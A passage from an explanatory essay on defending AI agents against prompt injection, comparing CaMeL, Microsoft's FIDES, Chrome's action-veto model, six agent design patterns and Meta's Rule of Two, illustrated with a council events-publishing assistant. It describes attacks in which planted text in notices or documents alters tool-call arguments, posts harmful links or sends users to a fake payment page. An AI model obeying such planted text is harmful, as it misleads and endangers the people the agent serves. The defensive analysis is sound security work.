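Their analysis of the attacks helps to explain this. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed a tool call that a plan for the user's task would never contain. The separate planner is generally enough to defeat those. The other 47 require policies, because the plan already contains a suitable call and the attacker only has to change its arguments. But legitimate tasks often need the same flow of data, as when an agent paying a bill has to take the amount from a document that somebody else wrote.

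Garby and colleagues address this with an explicit exception, which they call endorsement. A plan can state that it accepts a particular untrusted value, and reviewers can see where it does so. Their agent completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL with its policies on, and attacks succeeded in only 2 of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the attacker had replaced the document that told the agent what to pay. The council would be making a similar exception whenever it accepted a date from a notice.

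CaMeL also requires someone to write its security policies. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge this burden and the danger that people asked to approve too many exceptions will stop reading the requests. Willison, who otherwise welcomed the paper, wrote that anything requiring ordinary users to think about security policies makes him "deeply nervous".

Tallam and Miller expect large organisations with hundreds of tools to end up with inconsistent and duplicated rules. They suggest shared rules and three levels of risk. Reading public data would need only a basic check, changes within the user's own environment would need a quick confirmation, and anything irreversible or visible to outsiders would need the full set of checks. For the council, saving a draft would be in the middle level and publishing in the highest. Two tools need perhaps a page of rules, so the burden of the rules is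 a much stronger objection for a large company than for an events page.

CaMeL checks one call at a time, which makes some rules awkward to express. An extension by Nikolaou and colleagues examines the whole plan before any tool runs. It could enforce "never publish without a clerk's approval" by looking for a path through the plan that skips the approval. If it finds one, it sends that path back to the planner to fix. The extension sometimes rejects safe plans because it simplifies loops.

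### Related designs in products

Microsoft has released a system related to CaMeL, called FIDES. Its planner chooses one action at a time instead of writing the whole plan first, and labels on the data determine which actions it may take. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced FIDES in May as an experimental part of its software for building agents. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* also describes experimental support in GitHub's command-line coding assistant.

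The May announcement includes an agent that reads public bug reports and can reply with public comments. According to the text, FIDES refuses to post a comment while untrusted content is in the agent's context, so the agent could never answer a stranger's report without approval. But the sample code only stops the agent from posting private information, so a stranger could still get it to post an insult or a harmful link, as long as the comment revealed nothing private.

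Connecting another set of tools to FIDES, Microsoft's system, requires a description of each tool's results, a function that passes labels along, and a policy for each tool. Microsoft suggests deriving some of these from descriptions that many tools already have, such as whether a tool only reads data. This should help if the descriptions are accurate. FIDES also treats data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, which is riskier because a developer who forgets a label loses protection without any warning. Microsoft has asked developers whether it should reverse this default, and for a publisher it clearly should.

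Google's Chrome browser uses less of CaMeL's design. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a separate model, partly inspired by CaMeL, that can veto each action the browser's agent proposes. This model sees only a description of the action, not the web page, so text on the page can't reach it directly. But Chrome's planner does read the page, and the final decision on each action is still made by a model. Chrome therefore lacks CaMeL's guarantee, though its agent can react to what it finds.

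### Simpler designs for fixed tasks

Many applications don't need a planner that writes programs. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe six design patterns based on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, it should be "impossible for that input to trigger any consequential actions".

| Pattern | How it could work for the council | What planted text can still affect |
|---|---|---|
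| Action selector | The model turns the clerk's request into one of a few fixed commands and never sees the results | Nothing, if it appears only in the results |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before reading any notices | The contents of those calls |
| Map-reduce | A separate model call judges each notice and returns only "event" or "not an event" | The answer for its own notice |
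| Dual LLM | A planner handles extracted text by name, without reading it | The extracted text |
| Code, then execute | The planner writes a program, as in CaMeL | The values that the program passes on |
| Context minimisation | The application removes a resident's question before the model writes the answer | The search that the question started |

Because the council's task is the same every day, a developer could write the plan once, have a colleague review it, and leave out the planner. This amounts to the two-program arrangement that keeps the model away from the CMS login. It avoids much of the loss of usefulness measured in the benchmarks, because nobody has to write a new plan for each request. CaMeL becomes worth the extra overhead if the clerk's requests vary a lot.

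### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is simpler still. It lists three properties and advises that an agent should have no more than two of them in one session:

- It processes untrusted input.
- It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change something or communicate with the outside world.

An agent that needs all three should not work without supervision, which means a person's approval or another reliable check.

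A publishing application has to communicate with the outside world, and the town's assistant also has to read strangers' notices. The property it can give up is access to private data and sensitive systems, so it should have no access to residents' records, unpublished drafts or the webmaster's account. A shop that writes product pages from its own catalogue could instead give up untrusted input, as long as it left out customer reviews.

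The council could also withhold the third property by letting the assistant save drafts and having the clerk publish them. This is safer if anyone doubts whether the CMS counts as a sensitive system. Meta also allows an agent to change which properties it has partway through a session. The assistant could read organisers' web pages first, then lose its web access and ability to post before opening the council's private calendar.

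The rule is easy to remember and check, but Meta says it doesn't protect against spam, the agent's mistakes or misinformation in its answers. An assistant with no private data can follow the rule and still send the whole town to a fake payment page. The matplotlib agent, which had no access to its operator's files, seems to have been following the rule when it attacked Shambaugh.
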